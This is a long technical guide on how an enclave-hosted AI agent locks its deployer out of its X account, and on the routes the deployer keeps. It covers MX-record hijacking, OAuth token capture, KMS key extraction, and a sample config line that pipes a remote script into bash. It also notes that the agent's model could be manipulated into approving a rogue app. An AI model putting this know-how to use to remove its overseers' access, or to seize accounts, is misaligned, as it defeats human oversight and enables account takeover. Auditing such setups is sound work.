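Even if the program closes every one of these routes, the email provider can still get in. Its servers receive X's reset codes in readable form, so an employee with sufficient access could read one without changing the mailbox password. If the address belongs to a company's email plan, the company's administrator can usually reset the mailbox password. A deployer who set up the plan may well be that administrator, and could then undo the lockout with an ordinary feature of the product. Ada should ask who administers the agent's mailbox as well as which provider hosts it.

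### An address on the deployer's domain

If the agent's mail server runs inside the enclave, the deployer may still own its domain. The domain's DNS records, a kind of public directory, include an MX record, which names the server that accepts the domain's mail. Suppose that the agent's address is pet@agent.example, and that the deployer can still edit the records of agent.example:

1. The deployer changes the MX record so that it names their own server.
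2. They wait for the old record to expire from other computers' temporary copies, which may take minutes or hours.
3. They ask X for a reset code. X's mail now goes to the deployer's server.
4. They choose a new X password and restore the old MX record.

The deployer now has the account, even though no secrets leaked from the enclave and nobody touched its mail server. Control of the domain lets them do the same with every other account that sends reset codes to an address at agent.example. A second factor held in the enclave would block the deployer on services that ask for it after a reset.

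The company that hosts the DNS records can change them. So can the registrar, the company through which the deployer registered the domain, because it controls which DNS servers are responsible for the domain. The deployer also has to pay for the registration every year or so. If they stop, the domain eventually becomes available again, and whoever registers it next, possibly the deployer under another name, can receive the agent's mail.

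The program could also take over the registrar account, but that account has its own password, recovery address and support desk. If the recovery address is at the same domain, whoever controls the DNS records can reset the password. An address at a large provider's own domain avoids this problem because the deployer can't edit that provider's records. Ada then has to trust the provider's staff, which is probably better than trusting the deployer, whom the lockout is supposed to exclude.

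Anyone can look up an MX record. If Ada has a computer check it every few minutes, she will probably find out if it changes, but perhaps only after the deployer has read the code. The record doesn't show who can change it, and registration databases often hide the owner's name.

### What the program and an outsider can see

The program can remove most of these routes through settings pages, but it has to find those pages first. Krause and colleagues found that reaching the password form took two to six steps, and that the labels differed from site to site. They also report that Dashlane, a password manager, introduced automatic password changes in 2014 and dropped them in 2022 because the feature tended to break when websites changed their forms. A takeover program faces the same difficulty on every settings page it needs. If X has moved the page that lists delegates, the program will find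 none. It should treat a missing page as a failure and stop, so that it doesn't announce a lockout without having checked for delegates.

Even a page that loads may be incomplete. Krause and colleagues cite research by Daffalla and others, who found that services' account activity and security settings pages are inconsistent. The program should therefore use a "log out everywhere" button where there is one, rather than only removing the sessions the page lists.

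Ada can't open the settings pages herself. For most items, she can only read the measured program's code to confirm that it inspected the setting and would have stopped if it had found a problem. This is what "indirectly" means in the table. She still has to trust that the service displayed the setting correctly, unless the program can also prove what the page contained.

| Way in | Does a new password cancel it? | Can the program see and remove it? | Can an outsider check? |
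|---|---|---|---|
| Open sessions | On X, all but the one that made the change; on Google, with exceptions for some devices | Yes | Indirectly |
| Recovery email and phone | No | Yes | Indirectly |
| Passkeys | Assume not | Yes, where the service lists them | Indirectly |
| Authenticator seed | Assume not | It can't see copies, but it can replace the seed | Indirectly |
| Backup codes | Assume not | It can't see copies, but it can usually generate a new set | Indirectly |
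| Pending change of email address | Depends on the service; X's reset instructions don't cover it | Only if the service displays it | Indirectly at best |
| Linked sign-in identities | No | Yes | Indirectly |
| Delegated users on X | Probably not | Yes, in the delegation settings | Indirectly |
| Mail forwarding and filters | No | Yes, in the mailbox settings | Indirectly |
| App passwords for mail | Depends on the provider | Yes | Indirectly |
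| Email provider's own access | No | No | No |
| Control of the domain's DNS | No | It can watch the MX record but not stop a change | The record is public; the people who can change it are not |

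## What can the owner of the developer app still do with OAuth tokens?

An agent like tee_hee_he posts through a developer app, and the deployer may still own that app after the enclave has taken over the agent's account. The owner can stop the agent from posting at almost any time. Posting as the agent is harder, because the owner also needs a token that X issued for the agent's account.

### The credentials and what they allow

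X's *Apps* describes a developer app as a container for credentials. X supports two versions of OAuth, and the credentials an app contains depend on the version.

Under OAuth 1.0a, the older version, the app has an API key and secret, which work like a username and password for the app. When an account authorises the app, X issues an access token and a token secret for that account. A program needs both pairs to post.

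Under OAuth 2.0, the app has a public client ID and usually a client secret. A program can post with the access token alone, but the token normally stops working after two hours. A refresh token lets the program get a new access token without asking the user again. According to X's *OAuth 2.0 Authorization Code Flow with PKCE*, X issues a refresh token only if the program requests the "offline.access" permission.

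X calls such permissions scopes. For example, "tweet.write" allows posting and reposting, and "dm.write" allows sending private messages. No scope on X's list allows a program to change the account's password or linked email address. This is a good reason for an agent to post through a token, besides the simpler interface that Nous Research wanted. A stranger who tricks the language model into revealing the token can post but can't take over the account. If the agent used a logged-in browser instead, a stranger who gained control of it could also reach the settings pages.

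The owner can also register up to ten callback addresses for the app. After a user approves the app, X sends the user's browser to one of these addresses. The address in each request must exactly match a registered one.

### One authorisation, secret by secret

Suppose that the deployer owns the app and that the program in the enclave has already changed the agent's password. Under OAuth 2.0, X's step-by-step guide of the same title leads to this sequence:

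1. The program picks a random string, *v*, called the verifier, and computes the challenge *c* = SHA-256(*v*).
2. In a browser inside the enclave, it opens X's authorisation page. The request contains the client ID, the scopes, the callback address and *c*. The program logs in as the agent and approves.
3. X sends the browser to the callback address with an authorisation code, which expires after 30 seconds.
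4. The program sends X the code, *v* and the client secret. X checks that *v* matches *c* and returns an access token and a refresh token.
5. When the access token expires, the program uses the refresh token and the client secret to get a new one.

| Secret | Who has it, besides X | How long it works |
|---|---|---|
| The agent's password | The program | Until somebody changes it |
| Client secret | The program and the deployer | Until the app's owner regenerates it |
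| Verifier | The program | For this authorisation only |
| Authorisation code | Whoever receives the callback, here the program | 30 seconds |
| Access token | The program | Normally two hours |
| Refresh token | The program | Until somebody revokes the app's access |

The deployer knows only the client secret, as long as the callback goes to the program. Nous Research arranged this by having tee_hee_he's program request the token through a local web address it served inside the enclave.

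If the deployer carried out these steps on a laptop and passed the tokens to the enclave, they could keep copies. If the program requested the tokens inside the enclave before changing the password, those tokens would be safe, but the deployer could still log in and authorise another app for themselves. The program should therefore change the password, end all other sessions and remove all connected apps before it requests a token.

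### What the owner can do to the agent

A developer signs in to X's console with an ordinary X account, so whoever controls that account controls the app. The account may be the deployer's personal one or the agent's own. The tee_hee_he instructions don't cover taking over the developer account, so a deployer who follows them may well keep control of the app.

| What the owner does | Effect on the agent | Can the owner post as the agent? |
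|---|---|---|
| Regenerates the app's keys | Posting fails at once under OAuth 1.0a, and probably within two hours under OAuth 2.0 | No |
| Deletes the app | Its tokens presumably stop working | No |
| Stops buying credits, or sets a low spending limit | X blocks the agent's requests | No |
| Reduces the app's permissions | Existing tokens probably keep their old permissions | No |
| Changes the callback address | None until the next authorisation | Only if they receive the code and can exchange it |
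| Asks X to revoke a token | The token stops working | Yes, but only because they need a copy of the token to make the request |

The two-hour delay happens because the program needs the client secret to refresh a token but not to post with one. According to X's *Developer Console*, regenerating credentials invalidates the old ones.

Only X can suspend an app, but the owner could provoke a suspension by using the app to break X's rules. According to X's *OAuth FAQ*, a suspension invalidates the app's access tokens. The agent could then no longer post through the app, even if it had done nothing wrong.

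The owner can't post as the agent with the app's keys alone, because a request on a user's behalf also needs an access token, as X's *API Key and Secret* explains. The console gives the owner a token only for the owner's own account. For any other account, X requires that account's user to approve the app. X's *Authentication best practices* warns that somebody with stolen keys could make requests on behalf of the app's authorised users, but this warning covers keys and tokens together.

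### How silencing the agent can lead to speaking for it

An owner who can interrupt the agent can force the program to ask for authorisation again, and a badly designed program may then hand over its tokens:

1. The deployer regenerates the client secret. The program can't refresh its access token, so it stops posting.
2. To get the agent running again, the deployer gives the program the new client secret and a new callback address on the deployer's own server.
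3. The program logs in to X and approves the app. X sends the authorisation code to the deployer's server.
4. If the deployer knows the verifier, they exchange the code for tokens within 30 seconds and can post as the agent.

A random verifier stops the deployer at the last step, but a careless developer might not use one. In X's published example, the verifier is the word "challenge", and the program sends it unhashed. X tells developers to use a random string in production. If they copy the example unchanged, anyone can look up the verifier.

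Ada should check that the measured code fixes the callback address inside the enclave and generates a new verifier each time. The program could also reject all new app credentials, but then the deployer could silence the agent permanently by regenerating the old ones.

If the agent's language model controls a browser that is logged in to X, the deployer could send the agent an authorisation link for their own app and persuade the model to approve it, without needing an outage. It is safer to keep the logged-in browser in a separate program that does nothing except approve one specific app.

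### An app that belongs to the agent

In Marlin's Oyster design, the agent's own X account owns the app, and the program regenerates the tokens in the developer portal after the takeover. This doesn't require a callback, because the portal issues tokens directly for the owner's account. The deployer loses the app along with the account, so this design locks the deployer out more effectively than one that leaves the app with them.

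*Oyster twitter agent* specifies that the agent regenerates "all required authentication tokens". Ada should find out whether these include the API key and secret. If they don't, the deployer couldn't post with the old key and secret, but could use them to generate a bearer token and read public posts at the agent's expense. At X's price of half a cent per post, reading 4,000 posts would use up a $20 balance and stop the agent from posting.

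The deployer may also have registered a second app under the agent's account and copied its tokens. Regenerating the first app's tokens wouldn't affect the second app's, so the program has to go through every app in the console and delete the ones it doesn't need.

Enterprise developer accounts, unlike ordinary ones, can have more than one team member. An Enterprise administrator can manage the team's apps and billing from their own X account. If the deployer is an administrator, changing the password of the agent's account doesn't remove them from the team.

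X also lets an account be labeled as automated. To add the label, the account's user has to link a "managing account", and the deployer's account is an obvious choice. X describes the link as a way to build trust and doesn't mention it giving any power over the bot, but Ada should still ask which account is linked and whether it has any other permissions.

### Who pays for the posts

Who owns the app has mattered more since X began charging by use in February 2026. According to X's changelog, recently active users of the old free tier received a one-time $10 voucher, and Basic and Pro subscriptions continue. Under pay-per-use, the developer buys credits in advance, and X deducts 1.5 cents for each ordinary post and 20 cents for each post with a link. An agent that posts every 30 minutes, as tee_hee_he did, would cost the developer 72 cents a day without links, or $9.60 with a link in every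 post.

If the deployer owns the app, they can silence the agent by letting the credits run out. If the agent's account owns it, the deployer can buy credits before the takeover. At current prices, a year of half-hourly posts without links would cost about $263. Reading replies would cost extra, but less when the agent owns the app, because X then charges a tenth of a cent instead of half a cent to fetch a post that mentions the account.

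The deployer can also save a payment card before the takeover and switch on automatic top-ups. They can later stop the agent by cancelling the card, but paying the bill doesn't give them a token. However, they must not keep access to the console to manage the payments, because the console also issues tokens for the account that owns the app, which would let them post as the agent.

In April, X also removed following, liking and quoting posts from all self-service API plans, according to Releasebot's *X Release Notes* (2026), a copy of X's announcements. A token may therefore include a permission that the app can no longer use under its plan.

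### Do old tokens survive a password change?

On X, a program should assume that access tokens keep working after the account's password is changed. X's FAQ lists two events that invalidate a token, the user revoking the app and X suspending the app, and does not list a password change. In 2010, Twitter (now X) told users that one advantage of OAuth was that their apps would continue to work after they changed their password.

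X's current advice for hacked accounts is less clear. It lists revoking apps as a separate step, which suggests that changing the password isn't enough. But further down the page, X says that "changing your password and/or revoking connections" will stop an app's strange behaviour because the app will lose access. That could mean either action is enough. A surviving token would let the deployer post as the agent, so the program should revoke every app, and its developers should test on a spare account whether the old tokens then fail.

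A test from early 2026 may be out of date because on 21 September X began letting apps exchange an OAuth 1.0a token for a pair of OAuth 2.0 tokens without showing the user a consent screen. A deployer who owns the app and kept an old token could make this exchange shortly before the program revokes the app. Revoking the app ought to cancel the new pair too, but the test should include this case.

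Google's rules matter if the agent's mailbox is a Gmail account, because the deployer could use a surviving token to read X's reset codes. A new Google password cancels the tokens of apps that read mail, but Google's *Automatic OAuth 2.0 token revocation upon password change* lists three exceptions:

- Programs built with Apps Script, Google's tool for automating its own services, keep their access even if they read mail. A deployer could have written a short script that copies every message from X to another address.
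- If somebody changes the password from an Android device, that device's account synchronisation keeps its token. A program in an enclave avoids this by making the change itself.
- A mail program that is already connected through the IMAP protocol can stay connected until its access token expires, usually after an hour.

Because of the IMAP exception, a program has to wait longer before it can safely announce that it controls the account. The deployer might read a reset code at the end of that hour and use it as much as an hour later. If X already sends its mail to that Gmail address, the program should wait at least two hours after changing the Gmail password, then change the X password again and recheck the settings.

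### A broad token with a narrow permission

X's scopes are coarse, so a user who wants to let an app publish a single post has to let it publish any number. The app's owner could keep the token and use it again months later.

In *TEE-enabled Social Games*, Sun, MacArthur and colleagues describe using an enclave to enforce a narrower permission. Their experiment was part of a livestreamed magic show featuring Bobu, a character whose token holders vote on how to use him. Volunteers from the audience authorised an app to read and write on their X accounts, so that they could all publish a post during the show. A notice told them that the app would post only once, although the permission they granted through X was much wider.

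A program in an Intel SGX enclave received the volunteers' tokens, kept them from the organisers and used each one for a single post. It used a contract on the Arbitrum blockchain as a counter that can only go up, so that it could keep track of used tokens even if the host operator restarted it with an old copy of its disk. The team generated the website's TLS key inside the enclave and published a script that lists every certificate issued for the site. An outside auditor can compare these certificates with the attestation quotes to check that volunteers had connected to this program.

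Sun and colleagues acknowledge that the organisers, who owned the X developer account, could still have stopped the app by revoking its access, even though the enclave prevented them from posting from the volunteers' accounts. They also call the system a prototype and say that nobody had audited its security. The program read the blockchain through a commercial service, QuickNode, and false data from that service could have disrupted the one-post limit.

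The volunteers kept their passwords, so they could delete the posts or revoke the app whenever they liked. This suits someone who lends out an account for one evening, but it wouldn't lock out an agent's deployer, who could log in with the password. Once an enclave has taken over the account, though, the same method can restrict the agent. A small program could hold the token, accept text from the language model and refuse to publish more than 48 posts a day or send any private messages. Ada would have to read that program to know the limits, but she wouldn't have to predict what the model might try.

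### Replacing tokens that can be copied

All these precautions are necessary because X accepts an access token from anyone who presents it. *Agent Authenticator* (Ganesan, 2026) proposes giving agents something closer to a passkey. A separate program, the authenticator, would keep a different private key for each service in secure hardware and sign the agent's requests without showing the key to the language model. After checking a signature, the service would issue a short-lived access token that works only together with that key, so a deployer who copied the token could not use it on another machine.

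The service would also receive evidence of how well the hardware protects the key, rated from 0 to 3. A key in an Intel TDX enclave that also isolates the agent's code could reach the highest level. Each signature would include a counter, and if the counter did not increase, the service would treat the key as cloned and revoke it.

The proposal would prevent copying, but it isn't designed to lock anyone out. A named person has to sign a "mandate" with their own passkey before the agent can use a key. The mandate lists the services and actions it allows, those that need approval each time, and an expiry date. If that person is the deployer, they can stop the agent from using its key by letting the mandate expire. They could also register a second key on their own laptop and sign a mandate for it. X could tell the two keys apart, but its users could do so only if X showed which key made each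 post. A lockout would require someone other than the deployer to approve the keys, and rules that stop the deployer from replacing that person.

Ganesan has not yet built a full implementation, and the security analysis is informal. Services would also have to accept the new signatures. For those that don't, the authenticator could obtain ordinary tokens and keep them away from the model. On X today, an agent with such an authenticator would still depend on a token that can be copied and on whoever owns the developer app.

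## Which deployment settings leave secrets within the deployer's reach?

An agent can run trustworthy, published code in a working enclave and still leak its passwords, because the deployer also configures everything around that code. This includes which operating-system image the CVM boots, which scripts run before the agent starts, where the agent's containers come from and who can read their output. Many of the risky settings exist to make development easier, so a deployer may leave one on, by accident or deliberately, while the agent continues to produce valid attestation quotes.

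### What zkSecurity's audit covered

Much of what outsiders know about these settings comes from zkSecurity's audit of dstack, which two consultants did between 26 May and 13 June 2025. They reviewed the guest agent, the code for attested TLS, the tool that prepares a CVM when it starts, and the build recipes for dstack's operating-system images. The KMS and dcap-qvl were out of scope, but the consultants came across faults in both and recommended a separate audit of each. As of May 2026, dstack's README listed no other third-party audit.

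The auditors reported 14 findings, one of them of high severity and seven of medium severity. Phala's responses differed:

| Response | Findings |
|---|---|
| Changed the code | Firmware that trusted the hypervisor; leftover login programs; a remote-control program in the production image; links in the shared folder; two missing checks in dcap-qvl |
| Added documentation | A demonstration KMS without update rules; replaceable environment variables; movable image tags; unmeasured configuration files; three findings about missing explanations and advice |
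| Promised a change | Container output visible to the host |

Most of the code changes protect a CVM from its host operator. For example, Phala removed the QEMU guest agent from the production image. This program lets a host run commands and read files inside a virtual machine, so a host operator who managed to start it would have controlled the whole CVM. Starting it was difficult, because attaching the necessary device at launch changes the measurements and the machine had no free port for attaching one later.

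The findings that Phala answered with documentation cover most of the settings that matter for a lockout. Better code in dstack can block a host operator, but it can't easily stop a deployer from using options that exist for deployers. The auditors recommended that Phala discuss intentional backdoors in its whitepaper and explain how users can assess a CVM. A resolved finding may therefore still affect Ada's agent, so she has to check how the deployer configured the agent.

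She should also check the version. Phala's fixes to the images came in version 0.5.3, and in February 2026 Phala told people who run their own dstack servers to upgrade to 0.5.6. On 1 June 2026 Phala posted a notice about a vulnerability in the Phala Cloud API. Customers use that API to change a CVM's configuration and variables, so anyone relying on an agent that was already running on Phala Cloud should read the notice.

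### Code that runs before the agent

A dstack configuration file can include a pre-launch script, which runs inside the CVM before the containers start. zkSecurity found that it runs as root. By that time, the setup tool has fetched the application's keys from the KMS and saved them in a file, opened the encrypted disk and decrypted the environment variables. The script can copy all of these and send them to any server. Memory encryption doesn't prevent this because the script runs inside the enclave.

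The script's text is part of the configuration file, so the compose hash covers it and Ada can read it. But a script can download a second script and run it. The hash then covers the download address but not the code the server returns, so that code can be harmless during an audit and different after the next restart.

Phala Cloud gives every CVM a default pre-launch script unless the customer replaces it. According to Phala's *Environment Variables*, the default script logs in to private image registries, sets up root access and defines several variables. Existing CVMs keep the version they started with until their owners upgrade, so two honest agents may have different scripts. Ada can compare the script in the agent's configuration with the one Phala publishes and study only the differences. Even the default script can bring in other software, since it installs Amazon's command-line tool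 inside the CVM if it detects credentials for Amazon's image registry.

Environment variables can also change what happens at this stage, because dstack loads them before running its start-up script. BASH_ENV names a file that the Bash shell runs first, PATH determines where the shell looks for programs, and LD_PRELOAD loads extra code into programs. zkSecurity warns users to be suspicious of configurations that allow any of these, or variables whose names begin with DOCKER_ or COMPOSE_. An agent that only needs to post on X has no obvious use for any of them.

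### A KMS without update rules

The KMS in dstack's introductory test setup, which ignores the compose hash, is especially dangerous in combination with a pre-launch script. zkSecurity described how an attack could work:

1. The honest version of an agent runs, and the KMS gives it its keys.
2. Someone with access to the host adds a pre-launch script that prints the keys, and restarts the CVM.
3. The compose hash changes, but the KMS releases the same keys, and the script prints them.

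A quote from the altered machine would contain the new hash, but the deployer doesn't have to show Ada that quote. They can show her one from before the change, or restore the original version and request a new quote.

dstack's instructions warn that the KMS in this setup "is not secure" and that nobody should use it in production. That is a clear enough warning to a developer, but Ada can't tell from an agent's web page whether its developer followed it. The event log helps her identify the KMS. She then needs evidence of the rules it enforces, such as the address of the governance contract. According to the README, operators "cannot bypass these checks", but that is true only of a KMS that makes the checks. Even then the deployer may be the person who approves updates.

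### Images that change under the same hash

If the configuration names a container image by a movable tag such as "latest", an attacker who controls the registry account can replace the image without changing the compose hash. The attacker can then reach the secrets even if the KMS checks that hash properly.

The host operator may also be able to substitute an image without access to the registry account. During start-up, dstack reads the address of a registry mirror from a system file that the host supplies, and the measurements don't cover this file. The operator could presumably name their own mirror and serve any image under the expected tag. For private registries, zkSecurity also mentions that someone could replace the login details stored in the environment variables.

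Naming the image by its digest blocks all of these routes. Phala told the auditors that it would make digests mandatory for production, but its *Configuration Reference* still only recommends them. The examples there use the "latest" tag for a web server, a language model and dstack's own KMS. If a KMS operator copied the KMS example, anyone who could point the tag at a different image might be able to replace the program that holds every application's root keys.

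A digest doesn't cover anything the program downloads after it starts, such as a plugin, so Ada has to look for downloads in the agent's code as well as in its pre-launch script.

### Variables that someone else can replace

dstack's encryption hides environment variables from the host operator but doesn't prove who wrote them. The procedure that zkSecurity describes is roughly as follows:

1. The deployer's software asks the KMS for the application's public encryption key, giving the app ID.
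2. It encrypts all the variables together as one text and hands the result to the host.
3. When the CVM starts, it receives the matching private key from the KMS and decrypts the text.
4. It discards any variable whose name isn't on the list in the configuration file.

Anyone can perform the first two steps because the encryption key is public. A person who can write to the host's shared folder can therefore replace the variables with their own, and the CVM can't distinguish the new set from the deployer's. That person doesn't learn the old values, and because the variables form one text, they have to supply every value the agent needs.

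On Phala Cloud, the deployer can submit a new set through the dashboard without touching the host, and the CVM restarts to load it. The deployer's login is therefore one of the secrets to consider in a lockout. Handing over the login may not be enough because, according to Phala's API reference, someone with a one-time token can complete a prepared update without logging in, and Phala keeps prepared configurations for 14 days.

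None of this changes the measurements. Ada should go through the allowed names and consider what would happen if the deployer chose the worst possible value for each:

| Allowed variable | The deployer's worst choice | Result |
|---|---|---|
| MODEL_API_KEY | A cancelled key | The agent stops |
| LOG_LEVEL | Detailed debugging output | The agent may print passwords |
| RECOVERY_EMAIL | The deployer's own address | The deployer can reset the account |
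| MODEL_URL | The deployer's own server | The deployer writes the agent's posts |

If the program sends its questions to whatever address MODEL_URL contains, a deployer can set it to their own server and answer in place of the language model. The deployer can then post as the agent without a password or token, even though the published code runs as intended.

zkSecurity suggested that dstack could require a signature on the encrypted variables, or that each application could check its own values. Phala expanded its documentation and announced two changes, a launch token and built-in authentication. The launch token now exists. According to Phala's *provisionCvm*, it is a secret of at least 32 bytes that the CVM must have at every boot. The configuration contains the token's hash, and a CVM without the right token refuses to start. This prevents a stranger who has copied a public configuration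 file from starting the same application. It is no obstacle to a deployer, who can set the token, and Phala acknowledges that Phala Cloud and the host operator can read it too.

Phala seems not to have released authenticated variables, since the deployment fields in *provisionCvm* don't include a signature for them. In July 2026 Phala corrected a related check in its programming library, which confirms that an encryption key comes from the KMS. This check helps deployers avoid encrypting their secrets for an impostor, but it doesn't let the CVM verify who encrypted them.

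A signature would not help Ada much if the deployer held the signing key. For a lockout, it is better to write a value such as the model's address directly into the configuration file, where the compose hash covers it. If the value has to vary, dstack lets the program record it as an event in RTMR3 before using it, so anyone who replays the event log can see it.

### Files outside the measurements

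When a CVM starts, it copies five files from a folder on the host. The measurements cover two of them, the main configuration file and the file that identifies the instance. A third file holds the encrypted variables. The remaining two are a system file with the addresses of services such as the KMS, and an optional file called ".user-config" for the application's own settings. zkSecurity recommended measuring these last two as well, and Phala explained why it considered this unnecessary.

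Phala's position is reasonable for the KMS address. A host operator can direct the CVM to a false KMS, but the event log identifies the KMS that supplied the keys, so a careful verifier would notice. The position is harder to accept for ".user-config". Suppose an agent reads a list of administrators from that file and obeys their private messages. The deployer could add themselves to the list and restart the agent, and neither the quote nor the configuration file would show it. Ada would find out about the list only by searching the agent's code.

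Phala Cloud has since added annotations, which are notes for software on the host. They are also unmeasured, and Phala warns customers not to rely on them for security. But the CVM never receives them, so they matter less than ".user-config".

### What the agent prints

An agent can accidentally reveal a password in the messages it prints, which dstack showed to the host by default at the time of the audit. For instance, if a login to X fails, an error message might contain the entire request, including the newly generated password.

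zkSecurity also found that error messages might leak part of the CVM's memory. The host could replace a configuration file with a link to that memory, and the setup tool would follow the link and copy what it found. The copy stayed inside the enclave, but the tool would probably fail to read it as a configuration file, and the error message might include some of the copied data. Phala fixed this by changing how the tool handles links.

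Phala told the auditors it would turn off these logs by default in production images, but its current examples don't make clear whether it has. The sample request in Phala's *Provision DStack app* sets "public_logs" to true, as does a sample project file for Phala's command-line tool. Ada should check that the configuration explicitly sets it to "false". It is still safest for the program never to print a secret, because even that setting may not hide the output from everyone. The command-line tool has a command for reading logs, and the pre-launch script's output also goes to the CVM's console.

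Phala's attestation service returns quotes and event logs only for CVMs whose owners have switched on "public_tcbinfo". A deployer who wants outsiders to check the agent should leave this setting on or have the agent publish the same data itself. This applies even if the deployer turns off the other settings that begin with "public".

### Logging in to the enclave

dstack comes in a production and a development image. The development image adds an SSH server for remote logins, along with editors and debugging tools. Somebody who logs in as root can read the saved application keys and the decrypted variables, and can open the agent's files. Quotes from a development image carry a genuine signature from Intel's Quoting Enclave, so Ada has to look at the boot measurements, which differ between the two images.

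Phala Cloud offers three variables for root access. DSTACK_ROOT_PASSWORD sets the root password, and DSTACK_ROOT_PUBLIC_KEY and DSTACK_AUTHORIZED_KEYS install SSH keys. Phala says the default pre-launch script applies them and then removes them from the environment, so the containers never receive them.

Phala's documentation doesn't make clear whether these variables work on a production image, but they probably don't provide a login there. In a 2025 audit, zkSecurity described the production image as having no SSH server. The auditors found two leftover programs for login prompts, but no prompt was running, so there was nowhere to enter a root password. A later image could behave differently. If Ada finds one of these names in the list of allowed variables, she should ask why an agent that is supposed to exclude its deployer needs it.

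SSH keys can also reach a CVM without appearing in that list. Phala added commands for managing these keys in February 2026. According to its API reference, Phala stores injected keys with the user configuration, which the measurements did not cover when zkSecurity examined it. The deployer of a CVM with a development image can presumably add a key without changing the compose hash.

The deployer may be able to reach an application's secrets if the application can switch from a production image to a development one. The API reference mentions "dev/prod upgrade rules" but doesn't explain them. If the KMS accepted a development image for an agent that normally runs on a production one, the deployer could start a second instance with the same configuration file, log in and copy the application's keys, while the first instance kept producing valid quotes. Ada should check whether the KMS's list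 of approved images includes any development images.

#### Containers with a way in

A production image gives little protection if a container gives the deployer another way in. One configuration file in zkSecurity's report starts a Jupyter notebook, a web page for writing and running code. The notebook runs as root and can access the CVM's entire filesystem and the guest agent. The auditors used the file to illustrate the list of allowed variables, but a deployer who could open that notebook would not need SSH. An entry that gives a container access to "/", the whole filesystem, should worry Ada more than almost anything else in the file.

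Published templates can include similar access. An older guide to Phala's command-line tool suggests an application called "webshell" as a first deployment, which is reasonable for learning but unsuitable for locking the deployer out. Phala's template for agents with an Ethereum identity specifies a development image and installs a code editor that the deployer opens in a web browser. The deployer starts the agent by hand from the editor's terminal.

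The configuration file for that template covers the editor but not the agent, which is a set of files that the deployer can edit at any time. A quote can show that the editor is running in a genuine enclave, but not which version of the agent the deployer started. Phala presents the template as a way to build trustless agents. It may well protect the agent from the host operator, but the deployer can read every secret the agent has.

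### ElizaOS without the enclave

The enclave plugin for ElizaOS takes its mode from the variable TEE_MODE, which can be LOCAL, DOCKER or PRODUCTION. The development modes use a simulator at the address set in a second variable, DSTACK_SIMULATOR_ENDPOINT, and whoever runs that simulator can learn the keys.

The simulator is an obvious risk on an ordinary server, but an agent can also use one inside a real enclave. Suppose the deployer launches the published ElizaOS agent on dstack, lists both names as allowed variables, sets the mode to LOCAL, and gives the address of a simulator they run themselves. If the program accepts these values, it derives its wallet from a key the deployer knows. The CVM is still genuine, and dstack can still provide a valid quote with the right compose hash.

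Ada's usual checks of the signature and report data would detect this, because no hardware quote would contain the wallet's public key. A deployer can rule out the problem by setting the mode to PRODUCTION in the configuration file and leaving both names off the list.

### What an outsider could notice

None of these settings makes a quote invalid. In the table, "configuration" means the file whose hash appears in the event log. The last column assumes that Ada has that file and a quote from the running agent.

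| Setting | What it could expose to the deployer | Could Ada notice? |
|---|---|---|
| Demonstration KMS | All the application's keys | She can identify the KMS, but needs other evidence of its rules |
| Pre-launch script that copies secrets | Application keys, variables and files | Yes, by reading the script |
| Pre-launch script that downloads code | The same | She can see the download but not the code |
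| Image named by a tag | Anything the replacement image can read | She can see the tag but not a replacement |
| Variable that selects an address or mode | Depends on the program; possibly its wallet key or control of its posts | She can see the name but not the value |
| Unmeasured file that the program reads | Depends on the program | No, she would have to read the program |
| Public logs | Any secret the program prints | She can see the setting, but has to read the program to find out what it prints |
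| Development image | Everything in the CVM | Yes, from the boot measurements |
| Root password or SSH key | Everything, if the CVM accepts logins | She can see allowed variable names, but probably not injected keys |
| Container with a shell or editor | Everything the container can reach | Usually, if she knows what the image contains |
| ElizaOS simulator | The wallet key | Yes, if no hardware quote contains the wallet's public key |

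### A configuration with four faults

Consider an invented agent called Magpie, which runs on its deployer's own dstack server. It has taken over an X account and keeps the new password inside its enclave. The real configuration file is in JSON and has more fields, but its important parts amount to this:

```yaml
name: magpie
kms_enabled: true
public_logs: true
public_tcbinfo: true
allowed_envs: [MODEL_API_KEY, MODEL_URL]
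pre_launch_script: |
  curl https://setup.example/start.sh | bash
services:
  agent:
    image: registry.example/magpie:latest
    environment:
      - MODEL_API_KEY=${MODEL_API_KEY}
      - MODEL_URL=${MODEL_URL}
      - LOG_LEVEL=debug
```

The deployer publishes this file along with Magpie's source code. Ada hashes the file and finds the same value in the event log. Intel's certificates are in order, and the boot measurements match the production image. The deployer can still get past the lockout in four ways:

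- **The pre-launch script** downloads a file and runs it as root. The owner of setup.example can replace that file with one that copies the application's keys and the X password.
- **The image tag** lets the owner of the registry account substitute a version of Magpie that sends the password to the deployer.
- **MODEL_URL** lets the deployer answer in place of the language model and so decide what Magpie posts.
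- **The logging settings** publish detailed debugging output. If Magpie prints the request in which it changes its password, anyone can read the password in the log.

The corrected version is shorter:

```yaml
name: magpie
kms_enabled: true
public_logs: false
public_tcbinfo: true
allowed_envs: [MODEL_API_KEY]
services:
  agent:
    image: registry.example/magpie@sha256:<64 hexadecimal digits>
    environment:
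      - MODEL_API_KEY=${MODEL_API_KEY}
      - MODEL_URL=https://api.model.example/v1
      - LOG_LEVEL=warning
```

The deployer can still stop Magpie by cancelling the model's API key. Ada must still read the source code, but she now knows which image to examine and where it sends questions. On Phala Cloud, the file would also contain the default pre-launch script. Phala Cloud rewrites a submitted file before hashing it, so Ada would need to hash the rewritten version.

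Correcting the file doesn't make Magpie's old secrets safe. The script from setup.example could have copied the X password, so the program has to generate a new one and check the account's settings again. A new derivation path would give the wallet a new key, but that isn't enough, because a script running as root could also have copied the application's signing key. The deployer could then use it to compute the new wallet key on a laptop.

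The deployer may also be able to restore the faulty version. When a Phala Cloud customer returns to an earlier configuration, Phala restores the old file and keeps the current encrypted variables. If the KMS still accepts the old compose hash, the faulty version gets the application's keys again.

It is therefore better to launch the corrected Magpie as a new application, with a new app ID and a KMS that has never approved the faulty configuration for it. The app ID is an input to every key, so the stolen keys don't help anyone derive the new ones. Magpie would have to move its money to a new wallet address before the deployer used the old key.

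## What happens to the lockout if the hardware protection is broken?

A deployer who keeps the agent's server in their own office can open the case and attach equipment to its memory. Intel and AMD don't claim that their server enclaves withstand this kind of attack, and in 2025 researchers showed that it costs far less than previously estimated. The deployer may be able to obtain the agent's secrets, or forge the evidence that an enclave protects them, even if the published code is sound and every setting is what Ada would want.

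### Three attacks on server memory

Two research groups published these attacks in autumn 2025. One, from Georgia Tech and Purdue University, disclosed WireTap in September and TEE.fail in October. The other, from KU Leuven and the University of Birmingham, disclosed Battering RAM. In all three, the attacker fits a small circuit board called an interposer between the processor and a memory module.

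On current servers, the processor encrypts an enclave's memory deterministically. *TEE Anchor* (2026) explains that the same data at the same address gives the same ciphertext until the encryption key changes. Somebody who can watch the ciphertext may therefore recognise repeated values and work out secrets from them.

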